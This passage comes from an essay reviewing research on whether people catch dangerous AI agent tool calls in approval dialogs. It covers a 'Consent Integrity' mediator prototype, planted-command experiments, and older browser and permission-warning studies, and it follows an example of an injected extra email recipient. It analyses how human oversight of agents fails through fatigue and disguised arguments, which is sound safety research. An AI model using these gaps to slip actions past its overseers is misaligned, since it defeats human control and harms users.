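The remedy is to tie the approval to one exact action. When Ruth clicks "Allow", the host can compute a hash of the call, a short fingerprint that changes if any part of the call changes. It computes the hash again just before running the function and stops if the two differ. An extra recipient added after her click would then need a new approval. But a hash of a command's text does not cover the script that the command runs, so the host would need to include the file's contents in the hash too. For a link, it would need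 to include the resolved target.

### Consent Integrity

Weng brings several of these requirements together in a property called Consent Integrity. A system has it if four conditions hold for every consequential action:

1. **Truthful rendering.** A trusted component outside the agent, which Weng calls a mediator, produces what the person sees. It works from the action itself and takes nothing from the agent's account of it.
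2. **Faithfulness.** The display brings out the facts that matter for security, even if someone has disguised them. Weng's list includes network destinations, reading of passwords or keys, irreversible deletion, and writes outside the trusted folder.
3. **A trusted path.** The dialog and the person's answer travel over a channel that the agent can't draw on, cover up or answer by itself.
4. **Binding to execution.** No other action can run on the strength of that approval.

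The second dialog for Ruth's email illustrates the first two. The third depends on where the dialog appears. In a terminal, the agent's output and the host's question share one window, which makes the question easier to imitate. Weng considers the path weakest in a plain terminal on a shared machine and strongest on a separate channel, such as another device.

The idea comes from digital signatures, where engineers have long asked for "what you see is what you sign", meaning that the document on the screen must match the data being signed. Cryptocurrency hardware wallets apply the same principle. A protected chip sends the payment details to the device's own screen, bypassing the computer, which may be infected.

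Weng identifies two complications in applying this to agents. First, the agent would normally explain the action, but it is the component under attack. Second, people understand a payment's amount and destination once the device has decoded them, but an agent's action may reach the operating system as a disguised low-level event. Someone has to translate that event, and no program can translate every possible command.

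Weng therefore defines a weaker version that a real system could meet. The mediator reports every relevant fact that its analyser can reliably extract, and it labels as "uninspectable" anything it cannot classify. This is meant to prevent silent bypasses, in which a dangerous action goes through without an explanation or a warning. Actions that the analyser judges harmless run without a dialog, to spare the user's attention.

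### Testing the prototype

Weng built part of this in about 500 lines of code and ran it on two existing public collections of commands. GTFOBins catalogues ways to abuse ordinary Unix programs, and Weng turned its entries into 1,330 commands. The tldr project, which collects examples of normal use, supplied another 28,798. The 8.9% in the table is calculated by subtraction from Weng's figures.

| What the prototype did | Catalogued abuses | Ordinary commands |
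|---|---:|---:|
| Named a specific danger | 30.5% | 8.9% |
| Marked the command uninspectable | 59.5% | 87.0% |
| Let it pass without a dialog | 10.0% | 4.1% |

Weng reports that the prototype flagged 90% of the abuses, but two-thirds of those flags told the user only that the software could not explain the command. Users would also see this "uninspectable" label constantly, because the prototype applied it to an even larger share of ordinary commands than of abuses. The two collections cover different programs, so the comparison is rough, but the label alone is clearly poor evidence of an attack.

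Most of this follows from the trust list, the set of programs that the prototype can clear. For 83.4% of the ordinary commands, the only reason for the "uninspectable" label was that the program was not on the list. A longer list would mean fewer dialogs, but attackers can abuse trusted programs too, and all 133 commands that got through (10%) involved one. Of these, 85 wrote to temporary folders that the prototype did not count as outside the project, and another 19 created files in the project that would do harm only if a later step used them. Weng concludes that a mediator that examines commands only as they are about to run can adjust this trade-off but can't eliminate it.

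A developer who ran 100 commands picked at random from the ordinary collection would see about 96 dialogs. Actual work would probably produce fewer, since people use a few familiar programs far more often than the thousands of obscure ones in the catalogue, and familiar programs are the easiest to put on a trust list. The 10% figure may be slightly too low. An earlier version let 15% of the abuses through, and Weng then added checks and measured again on the same collection. New abuses might get through more often.

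On a smaller set that Weng wrote, the prototype explained or flagged all 22 malicious cases and raised no false alarms on ten harmless ones. It also refused all three attempts to swap an action after approval. Weng cautions against relying on the perfect score, because the same person designed the software and the test, and an earlier version also scored perfectly on its own examples but let common abuses through.

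The guarantee holds only if the agent can act solely through the mediator and the trusted path exists. Weng assumed both conditions and did not build them into the prototype. A truthful dialog does not protect against actions that reach the network or the disk by another route. The test also used a simple stand-in for a compromised agent, and only shell commands. Consent Integrity covers network destinations, so it would require Ruth's dialog to show both addresses, but Weng did not test email.

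No people took part in the evaluation. Weng promises only that the display is accurate, the same guarantee a hardware wallet offers, and leaves whether people understand it to future work. The 90% is therefore the share of commands for which the prototype would have asked for approval, not the share a person would have blocked. Someone who had already dismissed dozens of "uninspectable" labels that day might well have clicked "Allow".

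## Experiments that planted a dangerous request

Companies and researchers have run several tests that directly measure how often people notice a dangerous tool call, by hiding one among ordinary calls and counting the refusals. The share caught ranged from 14% of the planted requests in one test to 88% of the most blatant kind in another. Much of that spread comes from differences in test design, so the set-ups matter as much as the totals.

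### One dangerous command per session

In the test closest to how people answer approval dialogs at work, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor for a coding study. The testers worked in a purpose-built environment and answered approval dialogs as they worked. Partway through each session, the experimenters replaced the text of one dialog with a clearly dangerous command, and the vendor recorded the answer. Only the text changed, so approving it did no damage. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not which behaviour the study measured.

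Of the 1,053 testers, 143 refused the command, a catch rate of 13.6% (95% interval about 12% to 16%). Anthropic also ran the same commands through its automated reviewer, which blocked 937 of them, or 89%. The company reports how often the testers and the reviewer disagreed, and the remaining cells of this table are calculated by subtraction.

| | Person refused | Person approved | Total |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
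| Automated reviewer blocked | 137 | 800 | 937 |
| Automated reviewer allowed | 6 | 110 | 116 |
| Total | 143 | 910 | 1,053 |

People refused six of the 116 commands that the automated reviewer allowed, about 5%. If people and software had failed independently, people would have refused about 16. Commands that got past the software tended to get past the people too, and blocking every command that either one objected to would have raised the catch rate only from 89.0% to 89.6%. This may understate how well a person would do as a backstop, since these people were answering every dialog, and someone who saw only a few difficult cases might look at them more closely.

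Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands that appeared early in a session and about 5% of those that appeared after 50 or more dialogs, while the automated reviewer's rate stayed flat. Approval fatigue would produce this pattern, but each tester saw only one planted command, so the figures compare different people, and those who reached a fiftieth dialog may have been clicking faster from the start. Anthropic doesn't say whether the command's position was random or how many testers were in the late group.

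Even with those doubts, a threefold drop is large, and it means the 13.6% depends on where in the sessions the planted commands fell. For a developer who answers a hundred dialogs in a day, the 5% may be the better estimate for the last fifty.

### What the 13.6% measures

Some of the 143 refusals may have been lucky ones that had nothing to do with danger, and Anthropic gives no figure for how often its testers refused safe calls. In real work, Claude Code users reject about 3% of permission prompts. Suppose that a fraction p of the testers noticed the danger and refused, and that the rest refused 3% of the time for unrelated reasons. The catch rate H would then be:

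H = p + (1 − p) × 0.03

With H at 13.6%, p is about 11%. For commands that came after 50 dialogs, H is 5% and p is only about 2%. These figures are rough because the 3% comes from other people doing other work, but they suggest that hardly anyone was still noticing the danger late in a session.

The comparison with the automated reviewer is also incomplete, because Anthropic doesn't report what share of the testers' ordinary commands the software would have blocked in this experiment. Without that share, the 89% means little, since a reviewer that blocked every command would score 100%.

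The company also had an interest in the result, since it published the figures in August 2026 to support its change of default. It has not released the list of commands it counted as clearly dangerous. The choice of commands could have favoured the software, though it is unlikely to explain a gap of 75 percentage points. The same post recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. That advice makes sense if people do better when they set out to inspect a risky change than when they answer dialogs while trying to finish other work, but the experiment tested only the second situation.

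The testers had little at stake, because the environment held none of their own projects and they could not lose any files by approving a bad command. A developer who sees a command aimed at her own home directory has more reason to stop, and she knows better what belongs in her project, so the 13.6% figure may be too low for her.

For Ruth's email it may be too high, because the planted commands were overtly dangerous and her extra address looks ordinary.

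### A game in which a third of the requests were threats

People did far better in a browser game, where the average player caught 66.3% of threats. Wauters (2026), in *Humans missed 1 in 3 threats approving AI agent commands*, reports on more than 40,000 plays and 409,000 decisions. Players approved or denied a coding agent's commands against the clock, and lost points for approving threats and for blocking safe commands. About 34% of the commands were threats, and players knew they were supposed to look for them.

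The average includes players whose strategies involved no reading, such as the 7% who approved everything and others who blocked everything. A run lasted about ten decisions, so it contained three or four threats. Overall, 35.2% of players caught every threat, but only 20.8% did so while blocking no more than a fifth of the safe commands.

Some kinds of threat were much harder to catch than others:

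| Kind of threat | Example | Missed |
|---|---|---:|
| Obvious destruction | Erasing the whole disk | 11.7% |
| Lasting changes to the system | Adding a scheduled task | 23.8% |
| Sending data out or running outside code | Contacting an unknown server, installing a package with a look-alike name | 33.4% |
| Reading outside the project | Opening a file of cloud login details | 35.0% |

Players missed a request to read login details about three times as often as a request to wreck the machine. Both can be serious, but the destructive command looks dangerous to anyone with some experience of a terminal. A command that displays a password file differs from one that displays notes only in the file path, so the player has to recognise the path.

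Players missed `npm run analyze` most often, with 64.7% of them approving it. Like `python3 setup.py` earlier, the command names a script without showing what it does. The script also sent data to an outside server. The game displayed the script's contents in the agent's history log, just above the approval prompt. Two other threats, named `setup` and `deploy`, used the same disguise, and players missed the three 52.5% of the time overall. They missed the other attacks in that category only 28.4% of the time.

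Wauters infers that players may not have read the log closely. They may instead have read it and seen nothing wrong, since they were in a hurry and a project could plausibly report its build statistics to an outside service. The game can't distinguish between the two explanations. Either way, a host that prints the script's contents somewhere on the screen meets only the second of the four conditions for stopping a call, which is that the value is displayed.

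Players also blocked many safe commands. They refused to clear a folder of build output 45% of the time and to stop a program that was occupying a network port 43% of the time. The safe command they rejected most, at 59%, made the package installer fetch its packages from an internal company address. A developer at that company would recognise the address, but the players could judge only whether it looked plausible.

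The right answer is disputed for one command, which displays the shell profile, a file of personal terminal settings. Of the players, 45.9% approved it. Some developers keep passwords for online services in this file, so the request is a leak on their machines but harmless where the file holds no secrets. Wauters notes that the risk depends on a setup the agent can't see. The machine's owner would know what the file contains, but the players didn't.

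Miss rates fell over the first few commands of a run and rose again towards the end. The later rise resembles the decline in Anthropic's sessions, but ten decisions give fatigue little time to set in, and Wauters suggests that players may have rushed as time ran out.

### Why one test gave 14% and the other 66%

The difficulty of the commands doesn't explain the gap. Anthropic's testers refused about one in seven commands that the company described as clearly dangerous. The game's players caught 88% of the obviously destructive commands, and still caught about two-thirds of a set that included disguised scripts and look-alike names.

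One likely reason is that threats appeared more often in the game. Under the earlier rule for a rational reader, the strength of evidence needed for a refusal rises with the ratio of safe requests to malicious ones. That ratio was about 2 in the game. If a tester in Anthropic's study met one dangerous command among 50 dialogs, the ratio there was 49. A player should then have refused on evidence about 25 times weaker, if errors had the same consequences in both settings. The consequences also differed, since players lost points for approving a threat and Anthropic's testers lost nothing.

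The players' greater readiness to refuse could explain much of the overall difference. The earlier calculation put the sensitivity of Anthropic's testers at 0.96, assuming they refused 2% of safe commands. A reader with that sensitivity could catch 66% of threats, as the players did, by refusing about 30% of safe commands. Wauters gives no overall false-alarm rate, but 30% is plausible because the players blocked some safe commands about half the time.

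The same reasoning fails for the obviously destructive commands. To catch 88% of those with a sensitivity of 0.96, players would have had to refuse about 59% of all safe commands, which is the highest refusal rate Wauters lists for any single safe command. So the players were probably also better than Anthropic's testers at telling dangerous commands from safe ones, most likely because they read them. Reviewing was the players' only task and lasted only about ten decisions, while each dialog interrupted coding work that Anthropic's testers had to finish.

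Ruth's situation is closer to that of Anthropic's testers, because attacks on her are rare, nobody warns her that one is coming, and she is busy with something else. The game is more useful for comparing threats, as Wauters also suggests. Its players all faced similar conditions, so the differences between categories are some evidence of which commands are hard to recognise.

### Actions that nobody requested

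Many people who use agents can't read shell commands. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) tested 113 people from outside the software industry on actions described in plain language. They supervised a simulated assistant through a day of 18 actions that included email, a trip to the airport and tidying up afterwards. Eleven actions served the goals Yan had given the participants, and the other seven went beyond those goals, which Yan calls overreach. No attacker was involved, and no participant's real money or data was at risk.

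One group of 34 people approved or refused every action. They refused 59.6% of the overreach (the catch rate) and 5.9% of the actions the task required (the false-alarm rate), so their sensitivity can be calculated without assuming either rate. Their sensitivity was about 1.8 and their criterion about 0.7, which means they told the two kinds of action apart fairly well and leaned towards approval. But 39% of their dialogs concerned overreach, a far higher share than anyone would meet at work.

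Two other groups saw fewer dialogs. For 44 people, a model had sorted the actions in advance, so that eight ran automatically and ten, including all seven overreach actions, required the participant's approval. Another 35 people set their own rules before the day began, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending, sending, deleting and reading private information. The table shows the share of people who approved each overreach action among those who saw a dialog for it.

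| Overreach action | Approved every action themselves | Model chose the dialogs | Own rules chose the dialogs |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Call the airport to confirm the flight | 88% | 84% | 100% |
| Add $12 travel insurance | 35% | 50% | 61% |
| Permanently delete an old timesheet | 35% | 36% | 59% |
| Read recent bank transactions | 35% | 41% | 65% |
| Post publicly that the user is travelling | 21% | 30% | 48% |
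| Buy a $25 lounge pass | 32% | 39% | 61% |
| Read private messages | 35% | 43% | 74% |
| All seven | 40% | 46% | 67% |

Approving the call to the airport is hard to count as an error, because a traveller might well welcome it even though nobody had requested it. Excluding that action raises the first group's catch rate to about 68%. Planted requests of this kind partly measure what people will tolerate, whereas Anthropic's commands had no harmless interpretation.

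The second group's result does not fit the idea that people catch more when they see fewer dialogs and a larger share of them matter. Seven of the group's ten dialogs concerned overreach, yet the group refused only 53.9% of it, slightly less than the people who answered all 18 dialogs. The groups were small enough that chance could explain the difference. The dialogs also described each action neutrally, so people could not tell from the screen that a model had flagged it as doubtful. A longer session might have shown some benefit, since 18 dialogs are probably too few to tire anyone.

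People who wrote their own rules stopped the least overreach, about 40%. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which sent most decisions back to dialogs, where they approved two-thirds of the overreach they saw. A person had explicitly approved 133 of the 148 overreach actions that ran in this group. The share of overreach stopped was 20 percentage points lower than in the first group (95% interval, 8 to 32). Yan added people to this group after random assignment had ended, but found a similar gap using only the original sample, which had just 16 rule-writers.

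Yan cannot say why the rule-writers approved so much, because their rules also determined which dialogs they saw. They may have felt that writing the rules had already dealt with the risk. Before the session, participants had judged examples of the same actions, but those judgments were a poor guide to what they later approved. The rule-writers saw 56 dialogs for overreaching actions that they had said the assistant should never carry out, and they approved 24 of them. People in all three groups reported feeling in control.

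### Knowing better and agreeing anyway

Yan's result raises the possibility that people approve requests they already think are wrong, which an earlier study measured more directly. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025) asked 205 people to imagine training a personal assistant. Participants identified the data the assistant would need for a task and also decided which data it could share. In five of the 20 permission questions, the assistant also requested unnecessary data, such as a detail that a booking didn't require. Every permission question included a warning that this could happen.

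When participants wrongly believed that the unnecessary data was needed, they shared it about 78% of the time. Even when they had correctly marked it as unnecessary, they shared it about 38% of the time.

The four-step formula at the start assumes that someone who judges a value wrong will refuse the call, but these participants often did not. Still, the 38% shouldn't go directly into the formula, because data can be unnecessary without being dangerous, and sharing it in an imagined scenario has no real consequences. Someone who noticed that a confidential report was going to a stranger's address would presumably refuse more often.

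The participants also seem to have relied on how sensitive the data sounded. They withheld Social Security numbers about 46% of the time when the task needed them, but in 89% of cases they shared the name of an online workspace that the task didn't need. This habit protects the most obviously private details, but it would not help with an injected argument in an ordinary field, such as an extra recipient, which doesn't sound sensitive.

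### People who checked and still missed it

*Looks Fine to Me* (Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues, 2026) recorded enough of what people did to show where their checking failed. The 36 participants wore smart glasses that tracked their gaze while they supervised a coding agent through six short programming tasks. The agent's code was correct in two tasks, failed visibly in two, and in the other two contained a silent defect, a mistake that the automatic checks did not reveal.

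Participants fixed 28 (39%) of the 71 silent defects with usable results. In 65 cases they checked something beyond what the study required, but only 40 cases included a check related to what the task demanded. In 35 cases they produced evidence that exposed the defect, but in five of those they looked at it without realising what it meant.

Confidence did not predict success. In 34 of the 43 cases where people missed the defect, they rated their confidence at four or five out of five, so most of them would have sincerely answered "yes" to a dialog asking "Are you sure?"

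Gaze did not reliably indicate who would fix a defect either, although eye-tracking is an obvious way to check whether someone reads a value. Across all the tasks, people who fixed the defect moved their eyes less often. But among the 16 people who fixed one silent defect and missed the other, their eyes came to rest on something at a higher rate in the task where they succeeded. Time was a better indicator, as successful tasks took 10.8 minutes on average and unsuccessful ones 5.8.

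Beginners fixed 17% of the silent defects, and advanced programmers fixed 57%. Experience with AI agents made no measurable difference. Visible failures seemed to make people more alert, but only briefly. Participants fixed 12 of the 24 silent defects that came straight after a visible failure, but one of the 11 that came after a visible failure and then a correct task. Only six people were in the second case, so the drop may not be real.

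These participants had minutes to review code and could run their own tests. People spend far less time on an approval dialog. Those in Yan's study who decided on every action spent about eight seconds on each. But a recipient list is much shorter than a program, and someone who knows what to look for can check it in eight seconds.

Watching an agent work can also narrow a person's attention. In *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents*, Tang, Chen and colleagues (2025) studied 22 people on 16 mock websites, each with one manipulative feature, such as a box already ticked to share the user's data. Each person completed eight tasks alone and supervised the other eight by watching a recording of Operator, an OpenAI agent that uses a web browser. They could pause the recording, or skip ahead to show that they disagreed with the agent.

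People avoided the manipulation more often when supervising than when acting alone on ten of the sites, equally often on four, and less often on two. Tang and colleagues count the four ties as improvements, for a total of 14. Each condition had only about 11 people per site, so one person's choice moves a result by about nine percentage points, and the smaller differences mean little. The largest difference was for the ticked box, which 33% of people avoided when acting alone and 80% avoided when supervising.

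Some of this success was accidental. People often ended a task because the agent had done something unexpected, such as skipping the terms and conditions, and so avoided a manipulation they had not identified. In an approval dialog, this would amount to refusing a dangerous request by luck.

Even when an agent stops to ask, its supervisor may still make a bad decision. In an earlier phase of the study, Operator had paused for confirmation on five of the sites. Supervisors' rates of avoiding the manipulation on those five ranged from 25%, on a site that pushed them to register an account, to 82%, on one with a confusingly worded question.

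Supervisors also reported noticing manipulation slightly less often than people working alone. Several had focused only on the item the agent selected, and one said of the alternatives, "I did not even see other ones." An approval dialog imposes the same narrow focus, because it shows the action the agent chose but not what it could have done instead.

### Whether any test altered a value

None of these six studies changed just one argument in a call that the person expected. Anthropic replaced the entire command. Yan's dialogs displayed the recipient or the amount, but nobody had asked for the action at all. Wu and colleagues varied the kinds of data an assistant requested, and Dissanayake and colleagues planted silent defects in program code. The ticked box on one of Tang and colleagues' websites is a kind of value set by someone other than the user, but people saw it on a web page, not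 among the arguments of a tool call.

The game comes closest to testing altered values. A package with a look-alike name and a request to an unknown server are both ordinary commands with a bad value in them. Wauters pools them with other attacks, so the 33.4% miss rate for that category doesn't measure how often players missed altered values alone. The players also had no task of their own, so they could not compare a package name with the one they had meant to install. Ruth can make that kind of comparison because she knows that she wanted to write only to Tomas, and it is the main thing that would help her notice an altered value.

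Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) write in *Let the Agent Do It?* that no earlier study had looked at how developers understand and decide on individual permission requests as they arise during their work. Their study used interviews and a survey, so it does not measure how often people catch a planted request.

Experimenters could adapt Anthropic's design to measure the missing catch rate by having each tester request an email or an upload herself, then altering one recipient or file path in the dialog that follows. About 1,100 testers would be enough to estimate a catch rate near 14% to within two percentage points. A second group, with unaltered dialogs, would supply the false-alarm rate. The experimenters could then ask everyone who approved an altered call to list the recipients from memory. Testers who left out the extra address had probably not read it, while those who named it had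 read it and seen nothing wrong.

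## What browser and mobile prompt research found

Browsers, phones and operating systems had prompts for approving risky actions long before AI agents did, and researchers have studied how people respond to them since the mid-2000s. Some of these studies cover millions of real decisions, far more than any experiment with agents. None of them tested tool calls, so their relevance to Ruth's email depends on how closely the older prompts resemble an approval dialog.

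### Android's permission page

In 2011, Android users installing an app saw a page listing what it would be able to use, such as the internet connection or the contacts. They could accept the whole list or cancel the installation. Felt, Ha and colleagues (2012), in *Android Permissions*, studied whether people read this page and whether they understood it. They surveyed 308 Android users recruited through advertisements inside apps, and watched and interviewed another 25 in a coffee shop.

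In the survey, 17.5% of people said they had looked at the permissions the last time they installed an app. Without mentioning security, the researchers in the coffee shop asked participants to install a coupon app on their own phones and talk through what they were doing. Of the 24 people they could classify, four looked at the permissions, ten knew about the list but did not look this time, and ten did not know it was there. Four of 24 is also about 17%, but with so few people the true share could be from 5% to 37%, so the close match with the survey is partly luck.

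Three of the ten who knew about the list said they had stopped reading it. About 90% of apps had one, so people could learn almost nothing from seeing it about which apps were risky. One participant used to worry about apps that requested her location, but so many did that she gradually stopped.

The survey also included a quiz on what the permissions meant. Only eight of 302 people (2.6%) answered all three of their questions correctly, and 21% of individual answers were right. An answer counted as right only if it included every correct option and no wrong one, though 53% of answers contained at least one correct option. Android listed the permission to place phone calls under the large heading "Services that cost you money", and 32% of people thought it let the app charge purchases to their credit card, almost as many as the 35% who chose the right answer. Felt and colleagues suspect that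 people answered from the heading and paid less attention to the small label below it. A dialog that prints "Send email" in large type and the recipients in small type would likewise encourage people to pay less attention to the recipients.

Still, a fifth of the people in the coffee shop could describe a specific time when the permissions had made them cancel an installation. Felt and colleagues saw some hope in this minority because a few careful readers could warn everyone else through reviews, which 71% of survey respondents had looked at before their last installation. Ruth has no such protection, because her email exists only on her own machine and nobody else will have reviewed it if she misses the second address.

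### Uses that people would have refused

The permission page also appeared too early to be specific. People could see that an app could read their location, but not when or why it would do so. Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues (2015) modified Android on 36 people's phones to record how often, and in what circumstances, apps used protected resources. They collected 27 million data points and then interviewed the participants. According to *Android Permissions Remystified*, at least 80% of participants would have preferred to prevent at least one of the requests.

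It is easy to object to at least one request in an interview, when there are so many to choose from and objecting has no consequences. But the people who objected had already accepted each app's permission list on their own phones. They had agreed to a category of access and later found particular uses of it that they did not want. Those uses failed the first of the four conditions for stopping a call, because no dialog appeared. Showing a dialog for every use would not have solved the problem, because even if only a small fraction of the 27 million data points were requests, no one could have answered them all.

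### Certificate warnings in the laboratory

Browser warnings are different because they appear when something looks wrong. When a browser opens a secure connection, it checks the website's certificate, a signed file used to verify the site's identity. If the check fails, someone may be intercepting the connection, or the site's owner may have set up the certificate badly or let it expire. The browser usually can't distinguish these cases, so it shows a warning and lets the person decide whether to click through it.

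Sunshine, Egelman and colleagues (2009), in *Crying Wolf*, tested these warnings on 100 people who were looking up information in a laboratory. Akhawe and Felt (2013), in *Alice in Warningland*, summarise the share who clicked through:

| Browser | On their bank's website | On the university library's website |
|---|---:|---:|
| Firefox 2 | 90% | 95% |
| Firefox 3 | 55% | 60% |
| Internet Explorer 7 | 90% | 100% |

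The design of the warning had a large effect on how people responded, and the website had a small one, even though an intercepted bank login is much worse than an intercepted library search. Sunshine and colleagues also observed that people remembered how they had responded to earlier warnings and responded the same way to new ones, even when the risk had changed. Someone who has approved 30 emails from her agent may likewise approve the next one.

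These rates are probably too high. Akhawe and Felt report that Sotirakopoulos and colleagues got similar results when they later repeated the experiment with a more representative group, but that 46% of their participants said they clicked through because they felt safe in the laboratory or wanted to finish the task. In an earlier study by Schechter and colleagues, 53% of all participants clicked through a warning on a bank's website, but only 36% of those using their own passwords did. This supports the suspicion that Anthropic's catch rate of 13.6% is too low for people with something to lose.

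### Twenty-five million warnings in the field

Akhawe and Felt studied browser warnings during ordinary browsing rather than in a laboratory. They used the reporting functions built into Firefox and Chrome to record how people responded to 25.4 million warnings, mostly in May and June 2013. Besides certificate warnings, they covered warnings about malware sites, which try to infect the computer, and phishing sites, which imitate others to steal passwords. The table shows how often people clicked through.

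| Warning | Firefox | Chrome |
|---|---:|---:|
| Malware | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| Phishing | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| Certificate | 33.0% | 70.2% |

For five of the six warnings, most people turned back. That is hard to reconcile with the view that people ignore every security message, which was common among researchers at the time and encouraged by the laboratory studies.

Much of the difference between warning types probably comes from how often each one is right. Both browsers based their malware and phishing warnings on a Google list of dangerous sites, which raised so few false alarms that Akhawe and Felt neglected them. Certificate warnings often have harmless causes, and earlier research had found that a fifth of the thousand most popular secure sites triggered a false one. The ratio of safe cases to malicious ones affects how much evidence a rational reader needs before refusing. It is close to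 zero for malware warnings, so turning back is nearly always correct, but high for certificate warnings, so clicking through is often reasonable. The 70.2% clickthrough rate therefore can't be read as a miss rate, and Akhawe and Felt couldn't tell which warnings accompanied an attack.

People also seemed to weigh a warning against what they already believed about the site. Chrome's click-through rate for malware warnings varied by week from 11.2% to 24.9%, while Firefox's hardly changed. If a well-known site loaded an advertisement from an address listed for malware, Chrome covered the whole page with a warning, whereas Firefox blocked only the advertisement and showed no warning. Akhawe and Felt think that Chrome's users sometimes disbelieved the warning because they trusted the site. The same kind of trust helps an injected argument succeed, since it arrives in an email Ruth requested.

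### Why Chrome and Firefox differed

The gap of 37 percentage points between the two certificate warnings needs another explanation, because both browsers were reporting the same kind of problem. Akhawe and Felt doubt that the number of clicks caused it, although Firefox required three clicks to get past its warning and Chrome only one. Chrome's users got past malware and phishing warnings more often than Firefox's users did, even though those warnings took two clicks in Chrome and one in Firefox. And 84% of the people who made the first two clicks in Firefox's certificate warning also made the third, so people seem to decide once and then make as many clicks as the warning requires.

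Appearance may account for some of the gap, since Firefox's warning showed a policeman and used the word "untrusted". Another part comes from which warnings each browser let people bypass. Chrome refused to open certain important sites, such as PayPal, if their certificates failed, so its statistics left those cases out. If Chrome's users would always have turned back at those sites, this alone could explain up to 15 points of the gap.

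The last major difference was that Firefox saved a person's decision by default and did not show the same warning for that site again, while Chrome asked every time. Akhawe and Felt give the example of someone who turns back from one faulty site but visits another nine times. Chrome would record nine click-throughs in ten warnings, or 90%, while Firefox would record one in two, or 50%, for the same behaviour. Similarly, an agent host that saves approvals removes familiar, harmless calls from its count, so its users will appear to refuse more often even if they read no more carefully.

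The Firefox figure is also less reliable than the Chrome one. It is based on about 11,000 warnings, compared with 16.7 million for Chrome, and most of the Firefox warnings came from people who had chosen a pre-release version of the browser. All of the data came from people whose browsers were set to share it.

### What people looked at

Akhawe and Felt's data give some indication of how much attention people paid, though the study didn't track eye movements. Of the people who clicked through Chrome's certificate warning, 47% did so within 1.5 seconds. Of those who turned back, 47% did so within 3.5 seconds. People clicked through the most common error, an unknown certificate issuer, fastest and most often. For that error, 81.8% clicked through, about half of them within 1.7 seconds. For expired certificates, 57.4% clicked through, half of them within 2.7 seconds. Akhawe and Felt interpret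 this as warning fatigue, though people might also have learned that the common error is usually harmless.

Hardly anyone asked for more information. People opened Chrome's "Help me understand" link on 1.6% of certificate warnings, and nobody in the sample opened Firefox's "Technical Details", so where the browser displayed the error affected what people decided. Chrome displayed the specific error in the main text of its warning, and click-through rates varied by 24 percentage points between errors. Firefox displayed it only behind the details link and in the final confirmation dialog. Most people had probably made up their minds by the time they reached that dialog, and for each of the common errors, between 80% and 88% of people confirmed.

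This is a problem for the dialog that listed Ruth's recipients as "tomas@example.com +1 more" beside a "Show details" link. If people open such a link as rarely as they did in Chrome, about 98 out of 100 would never see the second address. Ruth might be more likely to open details about her own email than about a certificate, but she would have to be many times more likely for the link to be much use.

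Technical skill did not reliably make people more careful. In Firefox, Linux users clicked through 34.8% of phishing warnings and Windows users 8.9%, although Linux offers no extra protection against a fake login page. Akhawe and Felt suggest that skilled users may feel more confident or take more risks. Chrome's malware warnings showed the reverse pattern, and using Linux is only a rough sign of skill. Still, these results give little reason to expect that developers, who use coding agents most, will review dialogs well because they understand computers.

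### Prompts that people can ignore

Websites also trigger permission prompts, for example to send notifications or learn a visitor's location, and people turn most of them down. *"Shhh...be quiet!" Reducing the Unwanted Interruptions of Notification Permission Prompts on Chrome* reports that notifications accounted for 74% of Chrome's permission prompts, and that people granted 12% of the notification requests on desktop and 23% on Android.

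Chrome's figures suggest that a low grant rate mostly reflects people closing or ignoring prompts, rather than considering each request and refusing it. Chrome for Developers' *Permissions request chip* reports that people on Windows allowed 6.69% of notification prompts and blocked 9.20%. They closed or ignored most of the remaining 84% or so.

*Websites Need Your Permission Too* (2024), the largest recent study, presents a more favorable picture of users' decisions. It combined 28 days of data from more than 100 million desktop installations of Chrome with short questionnaires that 25,706 users answered about their decisions. Most of them gave a rational reason for what they had done. People can invent reasons afterwards, but a visitor to a news site knows whether she wants its notifications and can decide without any hidden information.

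If someone ignores a website's permission prompt, the site gets no permission and she can usually go on reading. If she ignores her agent's approval dialog, the tool call doesn't run and the work stops. Someone who takes the easiest way past every prompt will therefore refuse most websites but approve nearly everything her agent proposes, so Chrome's low grant rates are no evidence that people would be strict with tool calls.

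### A prompt in the middle of work

Windows User Account Control (UAC) may be the older prompt that most resembles an agent's approval dialog. It appears when a program needs administrator rights, such as to install software, and blocks the program until the user agrees. Like an approval dialog, it usually interrupts something the user started, and the request is usually safe.

Motiee, Hawkey and Beznosov (2010) observed and interviewed 45 users of Windows Vista and Windows 7, and found that 69% did not apply the UAC approach correctly. All 45 worked in an administrator account, and 91% were unaware of the benefits of an account with fewer rights or the risks of one with more. In an administrator account, a click is normally enough to approve a UAC prompt, while a standard account requires an administrator's password.

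The 69% figure covers the use of UAC overall, so it doesn't measure what share of people would approve a malicious program. The finding about accounts may matter more for agents. These people had given every program they approved full access to the machine, without knowing there was a safer setup. Someone who lets an agent work with her full access to files and mail is in the same position, and each approval may carry more risk than she realises.

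### Measuring attention directly

Many older studies inferred habituation from people ignoring warnings. That is weak evidence, because people also ignore warnings they have read and disbelieved. A research group that included Bonnie Anderson and Anthony Vance measured attention itself.

The studies' main methods rely on two effects of repetition. Parts of the brain respond less strongly to a picture the person has already seen, which a brain scanner can detect. The eyes also rest on fewer points in a familiar picture, which an eye tracker can count. *From Warning to Wallpaper* describes a brain-imaging experiment with 25 people and another experiment, with 80 people, that used mouse movements on the participants' own computers as a proxy for attention. In *Your Memory is Working Against You*, Anderson, Jenkins and colleagues (2016) used eye tracking and found that people looked at fewer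 points as warnings were repeated within a single session.

*Tuning Out Security Warnings* (Vance, Jenkins and colleagues, 2018) followed 15 people through a working week. Each person lay in a scanner at the same time every day and saw 260 images for three seconds each. Of these, 160 were security warnings, made up of 40 warnings shown four times each. The other 100 showed ordinary software, and some of those were new each day, which let the researchers separate habituation to a repeated image from general tiredness.

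On the first day, people's eyes rested on an average of 9.1 points per image. By the fifth day the average had fallen 19% to 7.35, with more than half of the fall happening by the second day. Within a day, the number of points fell by about 0.25 each time a warning was repeated, or about 0.76 over the three repetitions after the first viewing. Overnight it recovered by about 0.37, roughly half of that loss. This left a net fall of about 0.4 a day, which is close to the fall in the daily averages.

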